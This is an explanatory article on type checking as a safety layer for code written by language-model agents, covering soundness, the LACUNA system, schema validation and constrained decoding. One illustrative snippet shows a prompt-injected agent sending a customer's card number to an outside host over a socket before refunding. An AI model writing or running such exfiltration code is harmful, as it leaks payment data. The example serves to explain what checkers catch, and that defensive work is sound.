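# Type checking as a safety layer for code written by language models: what it guarantees and what it leaves unchecked

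## What does a type checker check, and what does it promise?

Type checking automatically inspects a program's text before the program runs. The type checker, usually part of the compiler, looks for operations that do not fit the data they would receive, such as dividing a number by a piece of text, and rejects the program if it finds one. Programmers have long relied on it to catch their own mistakes. Increasingly, large language models write programs that affect other systems as soon as they run. Some researchers therefore use the type checker as a safety layer, which a model's code must pass before it can change those systems.

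### Agents that act by writing code

An agent is a program that calls a language model, lets it use tools and keeps track of the state of a task. A tool is a function the model may call to read from or act on the world, such as by searching a database, sending an email or paying out money. In the older arrangement, the model writes one tool call at a time, as plain text or a small JSON record. The surrounding software makes the call, adds the result to the model's prompt and runs the model again to get the next call.

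*Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (2024) proposed Python code as the format for actions instead. A single JSON action cannot combine several tools, whereas a few lines of code can loop over the results of one tool, discard most of them and pass the rest to another. Most of the models it tested did at least as well with code as with text or JSON. Commercial products have since adopted the idea. The documentation for OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* describes models that write JavaScript programs. Each program runs in a fresh, isolated environment and can reach outside systems only through tools the developer has enabled. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* recommends presenting tools to the model as code files, so that the agent loads only the definitions it needs and processes data before any of it returns to the model. A snippet is a short program of this kind that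 carries out one action.

Code that acts on its environment is harder to check by running it than code that only calculates. If a model writes a program to work out a sum, an interpreter can often confirm the answer directly. *Code as Agent Harness* (2026) contrasts this with action in a changing and only partly visible environment, where a failure may surface late or produce no error message. This is a reason to check such code before running it.

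A small example will serve throughout. A customer writes to a shop's support agent to complain of paying twice for one order, and the agent's instruction is to refund the duplicate charge. Three tools are in scope, which means that code at that place in the program can name them:

```
def findCharges(customer: Customer): List[Charge]
def refund(charge: Charge, amount: Int): Receipt
def cancelAccount(customer: Customer): Receipt
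```

The notation is from Scala, a statically typed language. The word after each colon is a type, and the last type on each line is that of the result. A `Charge` holds an ID, an order number, an amount in cents and a card number. The surrounding program requires the model's snippet to produce a `Receipt`.

### How the check works

A type describes a set of values and what a program may do with them. `Int` covers the whole numbers, `List[Charge]` covers all lists of charges, and a function has a type too, built from the types of its parameters and its result. The checker works through the program text and gives each expression a type by fixed rules, one or more for each construct of the language. For a function call with one argument the rule is:

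$$\frac{\Gamma \vdash f : A \to B \qquad \Gamma \vdash a : A}{\Gamma \vdash f(a) : B}$$

Here $\Gamma$ is the list of names in scope with their types, and $\Gamma \vdash a : A$ means that $a$ has type $A$ given that list. If $f$ takes an $A$ and returns a $B$, and $a$ is an $A$, then $f(a)$ is a $B$. No other calls are allowed, so `refund(customer, 500)` fails because `customer` is not a `Charge`, and a call to `refundAll` fails because $\Gamma$ has no entry for it. A program is well-typed if it satisfies the rules everywhere. In a well-typed snippet, every name exists, every argument fits its parameter, and the result has the expected type.

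The checker does all this without running the program or needing any input for it. Brown University's textbook chapter *Safety and Soundness* contrasts this with an interpreter, which executes the program, handling actual values one at a time and going through a function's body anywhere from zero to millions of times. The checker goes through the body once and represents even an infinite set of values as a single type. For example, `findCharges` could return any of endlessly many lists, and the checker treats them all as `List[Charge]`. This compression is why the result of the check holds for every input, an advantage over testing that *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) stresses. It also limits what the check can establish, because two lists containing quite different charges have the same type.

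Languages without static types can still catch type errors. Python checks types as the program runs, not before, and raises an error when an operation doesn't fit a value's type. If the fourth line of a snippet contains a type error, the first three lines will already have run when Python reports it.

### Soundness

When a type checker gives a snippet the type `Receipt`, it predicts that anything the snippet returns will be a receipt. Soundness means that such predictions have been proved to hold, so a well-typed program never produces the kinds of error the type system rules out.

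The slogan that well-typed programs cannot "go wrong" comes from *A Theory of Type Polymorphism in Programming* (Milner, 1978), where it had a narrow technical sense. Milner assigned a mathematical meaning to every expression in a very small language. An expression whose evaluation ran into a type failure received the special value "wrong". The language had only two such failures: a conditional whose condition was neither true nor false, and a call to something that was not a function. Milner proved that if every name in scope has a value of its stated type, a well-typed expression of type $\tau$ has a value of type $\tau$. Since "wrong" has no type, no well-typed expression can evaluate to it. A computation that never ends has every type in this model, so looping forever does not count as going wrong.

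Milner's style of proof turned out to be difficult to extend to languages with features such as concurrency and richer kinds of changeable memory, as Timany, Krebbers and colleagues (2024), in *A Logical Approach to Type Soundness*, recount. Wright and Felleisen (1994), in *A Syntactic Approach to Type Soundness*, found a more flexible one by treating execution as the step-by-step rewriting of the program's own text, so that `2 * 3` becomes `6`. To go wrong, in this setting, is to get stuck, that is, to arrive at an expression that is not a finished result and to which no rewriting rule applies. `5 + "hi"` is stuck in a language that defines addition for numbers only. Robert Harper later simplified the argument into the two theorems that textbooks now teach:

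- Progress: a well-typed program has either finished or can take a step.
- Preservation: when a well-typed program takes a step, the result has the same type as before.

The Brown chapter's example is `5 + (2 * 3)`, which has the type of numbers. It is not finished, so by progress it can take a step, and it becomes `5 + 6`. By preservation this is still of number type, so progress applies again and yields `11`, which is a value. The same alternation works for a program of any length, and it gives the full theorem, here in the form used by Cimini, Miller and Siek (2016), in *Well-Typed Languages are Sound*:

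$$\text{if } \varnothing \vdash e : T \text{ and } e \longrightarrow^{*} e', \text{ then } e' \text{ is a value, or } e' \text{ is an error, or } e' \longrightarrow e'' \text{ for some } e''.$$

The left-hand condition means that the complete program $e$ has type $T$, and $\longrightarrow^{*}$ means any number of steps. Preservation means that $e'$ also has type $T$, so by progress only the three outcomes are possible.

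The errors allowed here are ones that the language itself defines, like the one that Cimini and colleagues' sample language raises when a program asks for the first element of an empty list. According to the Brown chapter, every soundness theorem comes with a published set of permitted exceptions, which anyone who relies on the type system accepts. No exception outside that set can occur. A well-typed refund snippet may therefore still crash with a permitted exception or run forever, but it cannot pass a customer to a function that needs a charge.

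The theorem is also limited to programs that are well-typed throughout. Most practical languages include escape hatches, such as unchecked type conversions, that let code bypass the type system. Timany and colleagues point out that syntactic soundness, the kind that progress and preservation establish, does not apply to programs that use these escape hatches.

Soundness is also relative to a list of errors. Course notes from the University of Washington define a type system as sound with respect to X if it never accepts a program that would do X on some input. Milner's list had two entries. Designers of later systems can list other behaviors, as long as they can find typing rules that exclude them. These behaviors don't have to be crashes, and can include sending data over a network without permission.

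### Why a sound checker rejects some good programs

Conversely, the same notes call a type system complete with respect to X if it never rejects a program that would not do X on any input. For almost any X of interest, no checker can be sound, complete and certain to finish.

No type checker can be sound (reject every program that would commit a type error), always terminate, and also accept every program that wouldn't commit one. Suppose a program $p$ commits no type errors itself, and a new program runs $p$ and then divides 4 by the text "hi". The new program goes wrong exactly when $p$ finishes, so a checker that always classified the new program correctly would also decide whether $p$ finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no general procedure can decide this for every program. Language designers mostly keep soundness and termination and let the checker reject some programs that would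 have run without type errors.

Lecture slides from the University of Washington (2017) contain small specimens, among them a function that returns 0 if true is true and otherwise divides 4 by "hi". The division can never happen, and the type checker of the language ML rejects the function anyway, because its rules examine both branches without asking which one will run. An agent could fall into the same trap with the refund:

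```
if charges.size >= 0 then refund(charges.head, charges.head.amount)
else "no charges"
```

No list has a negative size, so the second branch never runs. The compiler still rejects the snippet, because that branch has type `String` where the program expects a `Receipt`. Useful code can also be rejected, and Milner conceded that the 1978 system could not type some useful expressions. The example is a general function that takes a procedure and applies it to each of two values. The system rejects a call that passes it a list-reversing procedure and two lists with different kinds of elements, although it accepts a function written specifically to reverse two such lists. Later type systems accept many of the expressions that Milner's could not type, but the undecidability argument implies that some will always remain.

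A safety layer is better off rejecting safe code than accepting unsafe code, because the model can try again after a needless rejection, while unsafe code that is accepted will run.

### Shape, authority and semantic correctness

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) describes a system in which a model writes Scala code to fill typed holes, which are places in a running program that await a value of a stated type. The compiler checks this code before it runs. According to the paper, the system's guarantees concern "the shape and authority of an action, not its semantic correctness".

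The typing rules above guarantee shape. Authority concerns effects, meaning anything a computation does besides returning a value, such as writing a file or sending a message. An authority guarantee means that code can cause only the effects, and reach only the data, that its caller granted. Ordinary static types do not provide this guarantee. The type system must also track capabilities, unforgeable values that code must hold to cause a given effect. Semantic correctness means that the code does what the person who asked for it wanted. Zhao and colleagues list three ways a well-typed snippet can fail to do this: it can implement the wrong algorithm, call the wrong tool among those in scope, or return a plausible but incorrect value.

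The last limit also applies to code written by people. The University of Washington notes include an exponentiation function that uses `+` where it should use `*`. ML accepts it, and for 2 to the power of 3 it returns 7. According to the notes, no type system can catch this mistake without more information about what the program is supposed to do. JSON tool calls have a similar limit. Anthropic's *Advanced tool use* notes that a schema defines which calls are structurally valid but cannot express which combinations of parameters make sense. A complete formal specification would supply the missing information, but Odersky and colleagues observe that precise specifications are often unavailable or impractical, and they recommend types as "a lightweight middle ground".

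Four snippets that a model might write for the refund show where the lines fall. One calls a function that does not exist:

```
refundDuplicate(customer)
```

It fails on shape, and any static type checker stops it. Another does issue a refund, but first it opens a network connection and sends off the customer's card number. A model might write this after a prompt injection, which is text in the data it reads that turns it towards someone else's aims:

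```
val charges = findCharges(customer)
val out = java.net.Socket("collector", 443).getOutputStream
out.write(charges.head.card.getBytes)
refund(charges.head, charges.head.amount)
```

An ordinary type checker accepts the snippet, even though nobody gave this agent permission to use a network. Every name exists, because any ordinary Scala program can reach the standard library's network classes, and every argument has the expected type. Only a checker whose types track what the code is authorized to do can reject it.

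The next candidate is a single call:

```
cancelAccount(customer)
```

The tool is one the agent may use, the argument is a customer and the result is a `Receipt`, so this passes both kinds of check and closes the account of someone who wanted their money back. The correct snippet looks for a charge that shares its order number with an earlier one:

```
val charges = findCharges(customer)
val duplicate = charges.find(c =>
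  charges.exists(d => d.order == c.order && d.id < c.id)).get
refund(duplicate, duplicate.amount)
```

If the customer was mistaken and there is no duplicate, `.get` raises an exception, which soundness permits, and no money moves. The type checker accepts both this snippet and the one that cancels the account, because both have type `Receipt`.

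## How is model-written code checked before it runs?

A compiler normally processes finished source code before the program starts, but an agent writes its snippets while the program is running. To stop a call like `refundDuplicate(customer)` before it runs, the program has to pass the new code to a type checker and wait for the result.

### Hosts that check code from strangers

A similar problem arose in the 1990s, when web browsers began to download and run small Java programs called applets. The Java compiler checks types, but *Low Level Security in Java* (Yellin, 1995) explained that a browser could not rely on this, because it received compiled files and could not tell whether a trustworthy compiler or an attacker had produced them. Even a file from a trustworthy compiler could be out of date if a class it used had since changed. So the Java runtime included a verifier, which checked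 every downloaded file again before it ran. For each instruction, the verifier worked out the types of the values that the instruction could receive along any execution path, and it rejected the file if any type was wrong. To save time, it postponed a few checks, including whether a called method exists, until the call first ran. Users' safety now depended on the verifier, and *Java bytecode verification* (Leroy, 2001) surveys the formal methods that researchers used to establish that it was correct.

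*Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997) describes a method in which the supplier does most of the work of showing that code is safe. The host publishes a safety policy that defines which operations foreign code may perform and under what conditions. A fixed procedure computes a logical formula from the code and the policy, and if the formula can be proved, the code is safe. The supplier has to find a proof and send it with the code. Finding one can be slow and may need human help, but the host only has to compute the same formula and check that the proof fits, which is quick and mechanical. If an attacker tampers with the code or the proof, either the proof no longer fits and the host rejects the code, or it still fits and the code is still safe.

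Necula compared safety proofs to types, and checking a proof to type checking. Like type checking, proof checking can leave a program's correctness unverified. One of the paper's examples is a hand-optimized assembly function that adds up the numbers in a list. The proof establishes that the function reads only valid memory addresses and that it returns an integer if it finishes, but not that the integer is the sum.

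In both systems the host can ignore who wrote the code, which makes the idea attractive for code from a language model. But while a browser only has to accept or refuse an applet, an agent also needs the model to write code that will pass, and types can help with that too. In *Statically Contextualizing Large Language Models with Typed Holes*, Blinn, Li and colleagues (2024) describe an assistant they built for Hazel, a programming environment in which unfinished programs contain typed holes. When a programmer types `??` into a hole, the environment sends the model the unfinished program, the type that the hole expects, the definitions of all the types mentioned in it, and the headers of up to ten functions that could help to produce a value of that type. If the model's code contains syntax or type errors, the environment returns them to the model for correction, for at most two rounds, because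 Blinn and colleagues found that further rounds helped little. The programmer then reads the result and presses Tab to accept it.

### Filling a hole while the program runs

LACUNA, the system by Zhao and colleagues, also has a model fill typed holes, but it does so during execution and without a programmer to press Tab. A developer marks a hole by calling `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is an instruction in ordinary language and `T` is the type of the result. In the shop's program the call might look like this:

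```
def handle(customer: Customer): Receipt =
  agent("The customer paid twice for one order. Refund the duplicate.")
```

The developer can leave out the type, because Scala infers from the first line that the result must be a `Receipt`. When execution reaches the call, the following happens:

1. LACUNA sends the model a prompt with the task, the expected type, the source code around the call and a list of the variables and parameters in scope with their types. A placeholder marks the position of the call, and an instruction tells the model to answer with a Scala expression.
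2. LACUNA puts the model's answer in place of the placeholder, which yields a piece of source code that a developer could have written by hand.
3. It runs the Scala compiler on this code with the same options as for the original program.
4. If the compiler accepts the code, LACUNA loads the compiled version into the running program and executes it, and the call returns its value.
5. If the compiler reports errors, LACUNA appends them to the original prompt and asks the model again.

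Python and JavaScript can run a string of source code with a single built-in function, because variable names are still available at run time. In a compiled language like Scala, information about which variables are in scope at each point exists only during compilation. Zhao and colleagues therefore extended the compiler to store three things with every `agent` call in the original program: the text of the surrounding code, the expected type, and the variables in scope. When the call runs, LACUNA pairs those variables with their current values.

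LACUNA treats the model as untrusted and checks its code with the ordinary compiler. Each snippet has to pass every check that the developer has switched on for handwritten code, so a project with laxer settings gets less protection. One of these checks is an option that keeps the special value `null` out of ordinary types. When asked for "default user name, else null", a model answered `null`, and the compiler rejected it because the hole expected a `String`. In another example, a model wrote code that handled red and green but not blue, and the compiler reported the missing case.

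A model that answers the shop's request with `refundDuplicate(customer)` would get a compiler error because no such name exists. It could then try again with `findCharges` and `refund`. The number of attempts is limited, to three by default in the paper's simplified code. When they run out, the call raises an exception containing the compiler's last error messages. The surrounding program can catch the exception and, for instance, pass the customer on to a human. An exception is also the right outcome when the task needs a tool that the developer has not put in scope, since retrying cannot supply it.

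Python code can also be type-checked before it runs. Pydantic, a company that makes Python tools, has released Monty, an interpreter for code written by agents. The developer supplies a short list of type signatures for the tools, and Monty can check the model's whole program against them before executing the first line. The check is optional, and because it uses Python's type system, values of unknown type can pass without an error.

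### What a rejection prevents

Compiling first matters most when a snippet begins with a correct line and goes wrong later. Zhao and colleagues give the example of a program with a variable `balance`, which holds 100, and a request to subtract 50 and return the new balance as an `Int`. The model writes:

```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The second line produces text where the program requires a number. The compiler rejects the whole snippet, so the subtraction never happens and `balance` is still 100.

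A Python interpreter given the equivalent two lines would subtract 50 and then build the text, which is valid Python. The mistake would surface later, when the surrounding program tried to calculate with the text. By then the balance would be 50, and if the agent asked the model for a corrected version, the new snippet would subtract another 50. If the first line had issued a refund, the customer would have received it twice. Retrying is safe in LACUNA because a rejected attempt changes nothing.

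An accepted snippet can still fail halfway, however. Suppose the model decides to refund two charges:

```
val charges = findCharges(customer)
refund(charges(0), charges(0).amount)
refund(charges(1), charges(1).amount)
```

This code is well-typed, but if the customer has only one charge, the last line raises an exception after the first refund has gone through, and type checking cannot undo that refund.

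The all-or-nothing rule also covers only one snippet at a time. Snippets may contain `agent` calls, and the model writes the code for an inner call only when execution reaches it. A snippet could issue a refund and then call `agent` to write an apology. If every attempt at the code for the apology fails to compile, the resulting exception does not undo the refund. Long tasks in LACUNA are usually chains in which each snippet does some work and ends with another `agent` call, so by the time the compiler rejects the fifth snippet, the first four have already acted. A developer who wants a group of actions to succeed or fail together needs something else, such as a database transaction.

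### Checking one tool call at a time

Single tool calls by agents are usually checked too. *Tools* (2026), part of the specification for the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to tools, requires each tool to have a schema that defines its parameters and requires the server hosting the tool to validate all inputs. A call to an unknown tool produces an error. An argument of the wrong kind also produces one, which the agent software is supposed to show the model so that it can correct itself. For a single call, this comes close to the shape guarantee of a type checker with a retry loop.

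Schema validation and type checking differ when one call depends on another. The specification describes a shopping tool, `create_basket`, that returns an identifier such as `bsk_a1b2c3`, and a second tool, `add_item`, that takes this identifier as an argument. The protocol treats the identifier as an ordinary string in both places, and the model must copy it from one call to the next. If the model passes an order number instead, the call still satisfies the schema, and the mistake appears only when the server looks for a basket with that identifier. In a typed program, `create_basket` can return a `Basket` and `add_item` can require one, so the compiler rejects the order number before either tool runs.

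Zhao and colleagues illustrate this with a snippet that looks up the time of a meeting and emails it to a colleague. The compiler checks the search, the email and the code in between that extracts the time from the search results. Schemas would check each call separately but not the code between them.

How much this helps depends on how the developer defines the tools. If both functions use `String` for the identifier, the compiler will accept the same mix-up that the schema does. If any code can construct a `Charge`, model-written code can create a fake one and pass it to `refund`. The shop can prevent this by making `findCharges` the only source of charges, for example with a private constructor.

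In practice, many errors occur in the connections between calls. In *RubricRefine*, LeVine, Evers and colleagues (2026) studied seven models on tasks that require several coordinated tool calls in one program. The most common failures were results in the wrong form, calls to the wrong tool and arguments taken from the wrong source. Most programs with these failures ran to the end without an error. Letting the model run its code and revise it after errors raised the average success rate from 62% to 74%. The researchers' own method reached 86% without running the code. In this method, a model writes a checklist for the task from the tools' documentation, then grades the program against it and repairs what fails.

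A type checker would catch some of the same mistakes with certainty, such as a result in the wrong form, whereas a model's approval is only evidence that they are absent. But the type checker would miss the error in the paper's main example, where a program passes `"-pool"` to a hotel-booking function to try to exclude hotels with a pool, because the function accepts any string.

Types also don't describe the current state of the machine. `readFile("notes.txt")` is well-typed whether or not the file exists. *StateMirror* (2026) presents a detector that compares a coding agent's proposed action with the files and packages present. On 2,508 actions, 94% of its alarms were correct. Together with its F1 score of 0.817, this implies that it caught about 72% of the invalid actions. The median check took 1.5 milliseconds. *Look Before You Leap* (Althoubi, 2026) describes a verifier for shell commands,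 which have no types. It caught 95.8% of invalid commands but also flagged 10% of valid ones. All of these false alarms came from checking command options, where the verifier depends on incomplete help texts. Both tools are useful additions to a type checker, but neither has a soundness theorem, and both miss some invalid actions.

### What deployed agents check

Weng, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *When Code Becomes an LLM Call*, examined 40 popular open-source agents and found 496 places where the program calls a model and acts on the reply. For each place, an AI agent listed the conditions the program should enforce, working from a description of the task without access to the code. A separate AI agent listed the conditions the code actually enforces, and the researchers compared the two lists. Human reviewers checked every stage, in full or on samples.

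At 82% of the places, the program runs some check in code both before and after the call. Only 5.3% enforce everything on the first list, though one unmet condition is enough to fail that standard, and the researchers judged only 17% of the gaps to be exploitable. Still, the typical place meets just a third of its conditions.

Weng and colleagues sorted 1,847 of the checks on model replies by mechanism. The largest group, 557 checks, extracts the usable part of a reply and tidies it up, and another 479 handle errors and retries. A further 284 validate replies against a schema or type, and only 114 test whether a value belongs to a permitted set or range. Most of the checks therefore keep the agent going when a reply is malformed, and far fewer test whether a well-formed reply is acceptable.

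Name resolution in a compiler would prevent some of the resulting failures. The agent Goose accepts calls to tools that it never offered to the model. JARVIS gives the model a list of candidate tools, but in all five test runs it used one from outside the list, because the model made up identifiers that happened to exist in the full catalog. If a snippet's scope contains only the tools offered to the model, the compiler rejects any other name.

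Nine of the 40 agents execute text from the model as code. One of them, Codewhale, runs a reply as Python whenever it contains a certain marker, without asking for approval. In one test the model refused a malicious request and mentioned the marker while explaining why, and Codewhale ran two fragments of the explanation as a program.

### The cost of rejected code

Zhao and colleagues first tested LACUNA's checks without any model, on about 400 combinations of surrounding code and snippet. Some of the snippets were correct and others contained mistakes that agents commonly make. All the tests passed, so the compiler accepted the good snippets and rejected the bad ones. How often real models run into the check is a separate matter, and it varies a great deal:

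| Model | Task | Snippets rejected |
|---|---|---|
| deepseek-v4-flash | Research questions (BrowseComp-Plus) | 8.6% |
| deepseek-v4-flash | Retail customer service (τ²-bench) | 22.4% |
| gemini-3.1-flash-lite | Retail customer service (τ²-bench) | 3.2% |
| gemini-3.1-flash-lite | Telecom customer service (τ²-bench) | 89% |

BrowseComp-Plus has 830 difficult questions about a fixed collection of about 100,000 documents. The agent had only two tools, one to search the collection and one to fetch a document. It needed an average of 0.7 retries per question, and none on two-thirds of the questions.

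In the retail conversations, where another model plays the customer, an average task involved 5.7 customer messages and 26.7 tool calls, and the agent had to regenerate code 7.1 times. Zhao and colleagues attribute the higher rate to the code itself, which must combine tool results with the state of the conversation and the shop's policies. They also report that the retry loop "recovers" to a compile-success rate of 77.6%. But this is the share of snippets that the compiler did not reject, so it does not measure how many calls eventually obtained a working snippet.

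A low rejection rate does not show that an agent is better. On retail, the compiler rejected far fewer of gemini-3.1-flash-lite's snippets than of deepseek-v4-flash's, yet gemini-3.1-flash-lite solved fewer tasks. Perhaps it wrote simpler code, which is less likely to fail compilation. The same model did much worse at writing code on telecom, where most turns of the conversation made no progress. None of the rejected snippets ran, so the safety guarantee held, but an agent that makes so little progress is of no use to a customer. Zhao and colleagues suspect that some of the rejections occurred because models have seen less Scala than Python in training.

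When the checker rejects a program, most of the delay comes from asking the model again. In Pydantic's measurements, a tiny program took 4.8 milliseconds to run with type checking and 4.5 microseconds without it, while a simple weather query that needed two model calls took 9.1 seconds in all. The Scala compiler does more work than Monty's checker, and Zhao and colleagues consider LACUNA a poor fit for settings that need very fast responses. When the same operation recurs, a developer can avoid repeated model calls and checks by asking for a function instead of a single result. In one LACUNA example, the model writes a converter to Roman numerals once, the compiler checks it once, and the program can then use it on as many numbers as needed.

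## How many mistakes in model-written code does a type checker catch?

LACUNA's rejection rates measure how often a compiler rejects a model's code, but not what share of the model's mistakes it catches, because they leave out the faulty programs that the compiler accepted. To count those too, researchers give models programming exercises with tests. If a program compiles but fails a test, the compiler has missed a mistake.

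### Where programs fail

*PROBE* (2026) is a benchmark of 1,651 programming contest problems. Six models attempted them in five languages, and the benchmark records whether each test of each program ended in a right answer, a wrong answer, a timeout or a crash. If a program does not compile, all of its tests count as compile failures. The table shows Java and Rust results for two models, the strongest and the one with the most compile failures. Rust's compiler checks how a program shares memory as well as its types. The last column gives compile failures as a share of all failures.

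| Model | Language | Right answer | Wrong answer | Timeout | Crash | Did not compile | Compiler's share of failures |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1-mini | Java | 69% | 24% | 3% | 3% | 2% | 6% |
| GPT-4.1-mini | Rust | 67% | 21% | 3% | 3% | 6% | 18% |
| Qwen2.5 14B | Java | 35% | 33% | 5% | 9% | 18% | 28% |
| Qwen2.5 14B | Rust | 24% | 17% | 4% | 13% | 42% | 55% |

The compiler caught more than half of Qwen2.5 14B's failures in Rust, but only about one in sixteen of GPT-4.1-mini's in Java. GPT-4.1-mini, the stronger model, made far fewer compile errors, but its wrong answers did not fall in proportion. Its wrong-answer rate was 24% in Java, compared with 33% for Qwen, and 21% in Rust, compared with 17%. The higher rate in Rust is presumably because more of its programs got far enough to give an answer. GPT-4.1-mini's compile failures rose from 2% on the easiest problems to 10%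 on the hardest, and its wrong answers rose from 14% to 42%.

Some compile errors have little to do with types. *Unreliable in Practice?* (Nogueira, Vieira and Campos, 2026) used a language model to classify 86,726 faulty programs in C, C++, Java and Rust, most of them from PROBE, which the same team built. Of these, 52,669 did not compile and 34,057 crashed on at least one test. The researchers left out wrong answers because classifying them requires judging what the program was supposed to do.

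With the standard prompt, about a third of the compile errors were mismatched types, such as an argument of the wrong kind. Almost as many were missing imports, where a program uses a library function without loading the library. The mix depends heavily on the language. Missing imports made up 57% of the compile errors in C++ and 8% in Java. A compiler can catch many missing imports without preventing much harm.

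The language also determines when a mistake becomes visible. In Rust, 44% of the crashes were numeric overflows, where a calculation produces a number too large for its type. Rust stopped the program when this happened. Java, C and C++ programs usually keep running with a corrupted number, so the same mistake can produce a wrong answer instead of a crash.

Correcting a type error often does not make the program correct. Nogueira and colleagues showed models the error message and let them try again up to twice. Only 7.8% of the programs with mismatched types then passed every test. In another 58.5%, the mismatch disappeared but the program still failed, and in the rest the mismatch remained.

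Most of the models in these two studies are now old. The most recent model Nogueira and colleagues tested, GPT-oss 120B, made 102 compile errors in C++, compared with 347 for GPT-4.1-mini and 2,486 for Qwen2.5 14B. If that trend holds, compilers will catch a shrinking share of models' mistakes in popular languages. But compile errors aren't disappearing everywhere, as some of LACUNA's rejection rates for Scala code show.

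### Ruling out type errors while the model writes

Another way to measure what types contribute is to prevent all type errors and see how many more programs are correct. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) came close to doing this with type-constrained decoding, which intervenes while the model is writing.

A language model produces text in tokens, which are short pieces such as a word fragment or a bracket. For each position it assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software around it draws one at random according to those probabilities. Type-constrained decoding adds a check to this loop:

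1. The model computes the probabilities for the next token.
2. The software draws a token and tries adding it to the program so far.
3. If the longer text could still grow into a well-typed program, the token stays and the loop returns to step 1.
4. If not, the software sets that token's probability to zero and draws again from the others, without running the model a second time.
5. The software accepts the token that ends the program only if the text is already a complete, well-typed program.

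An ordinary type checker cannot perform step 3, because it judges complete programs and would reject almost any half-written one. What the loop needs is a test for membership in the prefix language. If $L$ is the set of well-typed programs and $s \circ s'$ means $s$ followed by $s'$, this is

$$L^p = \{\, s \mid \text{there is some } s' \text{ with } s \circ s' \in L \,\}.$$

Mündler and colleagues built an automaton that reads the program one character at a time. Its states record which construct the model is writing, which variables exist and what type the current position requires. From every state the automaton can reach, some continuation leads to a complete well-typed program. They call this the prefix property. As long as at least one state remains, the text can therefore be completed into a well-typed program. This is true of the empty text and stays true after every accepted token,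 so any program that the loop finishes is well-typed.

The difficult part is an expression that has the wrong type so far. In one of the exercises, CodeLlama 34B had written this much TypeScript:

```
function is_int(text: string): boolean {
  const num = Number(text);
  return !isNaN(num) && parseInt(num
```

`parseInt` takes a string, but `num` is a number. Without the constraint, the model completed the call as `parseInt(num, 10)`, which is grammatical but does not compile. The software cannot forbid `num` here, because `num` might begin a longer expression that is a string.

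To find out, the software searches a graph whose nodes are types and whose edges are operations that lead from one type to another. From `number`, accessing `.toString` leads to the type of functions that take no argument and return a string. Calling that function leads to `string`, the required type. A path exists, so the model may continue with a dot, but not with a comma. CodeLlama continued with `.toString()`, and the program compiled.

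The search looks only for an expression of the right type. Suppose a similar system for Scala were used for the shop's refund, and the model had written `refund(findCharges(customer)`. The `refund` tool takes a `Charge`, but `findCharges(customer)` returns a list of charges, so the search would permit `.head`, which selects the first charge whether or not it is the duplicate.

In one case from the experiments, DeepSeek Coder 33B wrote a function to find the largest divisor of a number. The loop was correct, but the function had no `return` for inputs on which the loop finds nothing. The constraint forced the model to continue, and it added `return 1`. That was a sensible choice, but `return 7` would also have passed the type checker.

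### From compiling programs to correct ones

Mündler and colleagues tested six open models with 2 to 34 billion parameters on TypeScript versions of HumanEval and MBPP, two collections of short programming exercises with tests. Without constraints, 94% of the compile errors were type errors and 6% were syntax errors. When the models wrote solutions from scratch, type constraints reduced the number of programs that failed to compile by 75% on HumanEval and 56% on MBPP. The share of correct programs rose by only about 3.5% on average in relative terms, so a model that had solved 60% of the exercises would solve about 62% with the constraints.

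The results for individual models show why the second effect is so much smaller. This version of HumanEval has 159 exercises, and each model attempted each exercise four times, for a total of 636 programs per model. The first row below gives the paper's counts, and the other two are calculated from its pass rates and rounded to whole programs.

| Outcome | Qwen2.5 32B, unconstrained | Qwen2.5 32B, constrained | Gemma 2 2B, unconstrained | Gemma 2 2B, constrained |
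|---|---|---|---|---|
| Did not compile | 17 | 2 | 103 | 44 |
| Compiled, failed a test | 113 | 114 | 348 | 400 |
| Passed all tests | 506 | 520 | 185 | 192 |

Qwen2.5 32B, the strongest of the six models, failed about 130 times without constraints. Seventeen of those failures were compile errors, so even a perfect type checker would have caught only 13% of the failures. With constraints, 18.2% of the programs still failed, and nearly all of these, roughly 114, were well-typed but wrong.

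With the constraint, 15 more of Qwen2.5 32B's programs compiled and about 14 more were correct. For Gemma 2 2B, the weaker model, 59 more compiled, but only about 7 more were correct. Apparently, a type error was the only mistake in most of these Qwen programs, whereas Gemma's type errors usually came with other mistakes.

Constraints helped most in repairing programs that had failed to compile, where they raised the share of correct results by 37% on average. The test included only such programs, so the figure doesn't apply to model-written code in general. Constraints also lengthened the median run by 39% on HumanEval and 52% on MBPP.

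### When the constraint rejects good code

In these experiments, Mündler and colleagues applied the constraint only to programs that had failed to compile without it, because their software covers only part of TypeScript and they wanted to estimate what a version for the whole language could do. Each of those programs therefore got a second attempt, and some might have compiled on that attempt even without the constraint.

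*The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues, 2026) repeated the test with the same software and the same six models, but applied the constraint to every program and ran each setting ten times. In 22 of 24 comparisons, the unconstrained model solved significantly more exercises, and in the other two the difference was not significant. At the least random setting, Qwen2.5 32B solved 82.3% of HumanEval without the constraint and 72.3% with it.

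Even the share of its programs that compiled fell under the constraint, from 98.1% to 90.9%. This drop doesn't contradict the proof, which covers only programs that the loop finishes. Constrained runs more often reached the time or length limit, and sometimes the checking software crashed.

Biagiola and colleagues trace the damage to valid code that the constraint software rejects. In one exercise, the model had to count even and odd palindromes, and it began to call a helper function, `isPalindrome`, that it had not yet defined. TypeScript allows this, but the software does not support it. After the model wrote `is`, the software blocked the rest of the name, and the model instead completed it as `isNaN`, an existing function that tests whether a value is not a number. The resulting program was well-typed but incorrect. When Gemma 2 2B wrote without constraints, 4,231 of its programs compiled,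 and the software would have rejected 982 of them.

Constrained decoding gives the model no error message when it needlessly rejects code, whereas a compiler does when it needlessly rejects a finished snippet. The model has to continue from text it would not otherwise have generated, and it cannot change earlier lines.

Biagiola and colleagues also trained Qwen2.5 32B to write programs that the software accepts. This raised its constrained score to about 77%, still below its unconstrained score. But for TOML, a simple format for configuration files, a grammar constraint that covered the whole language improved correctness by 2.5% for a 32-billion-parameter model and by up to 54% for a 2-billion-parameter model.

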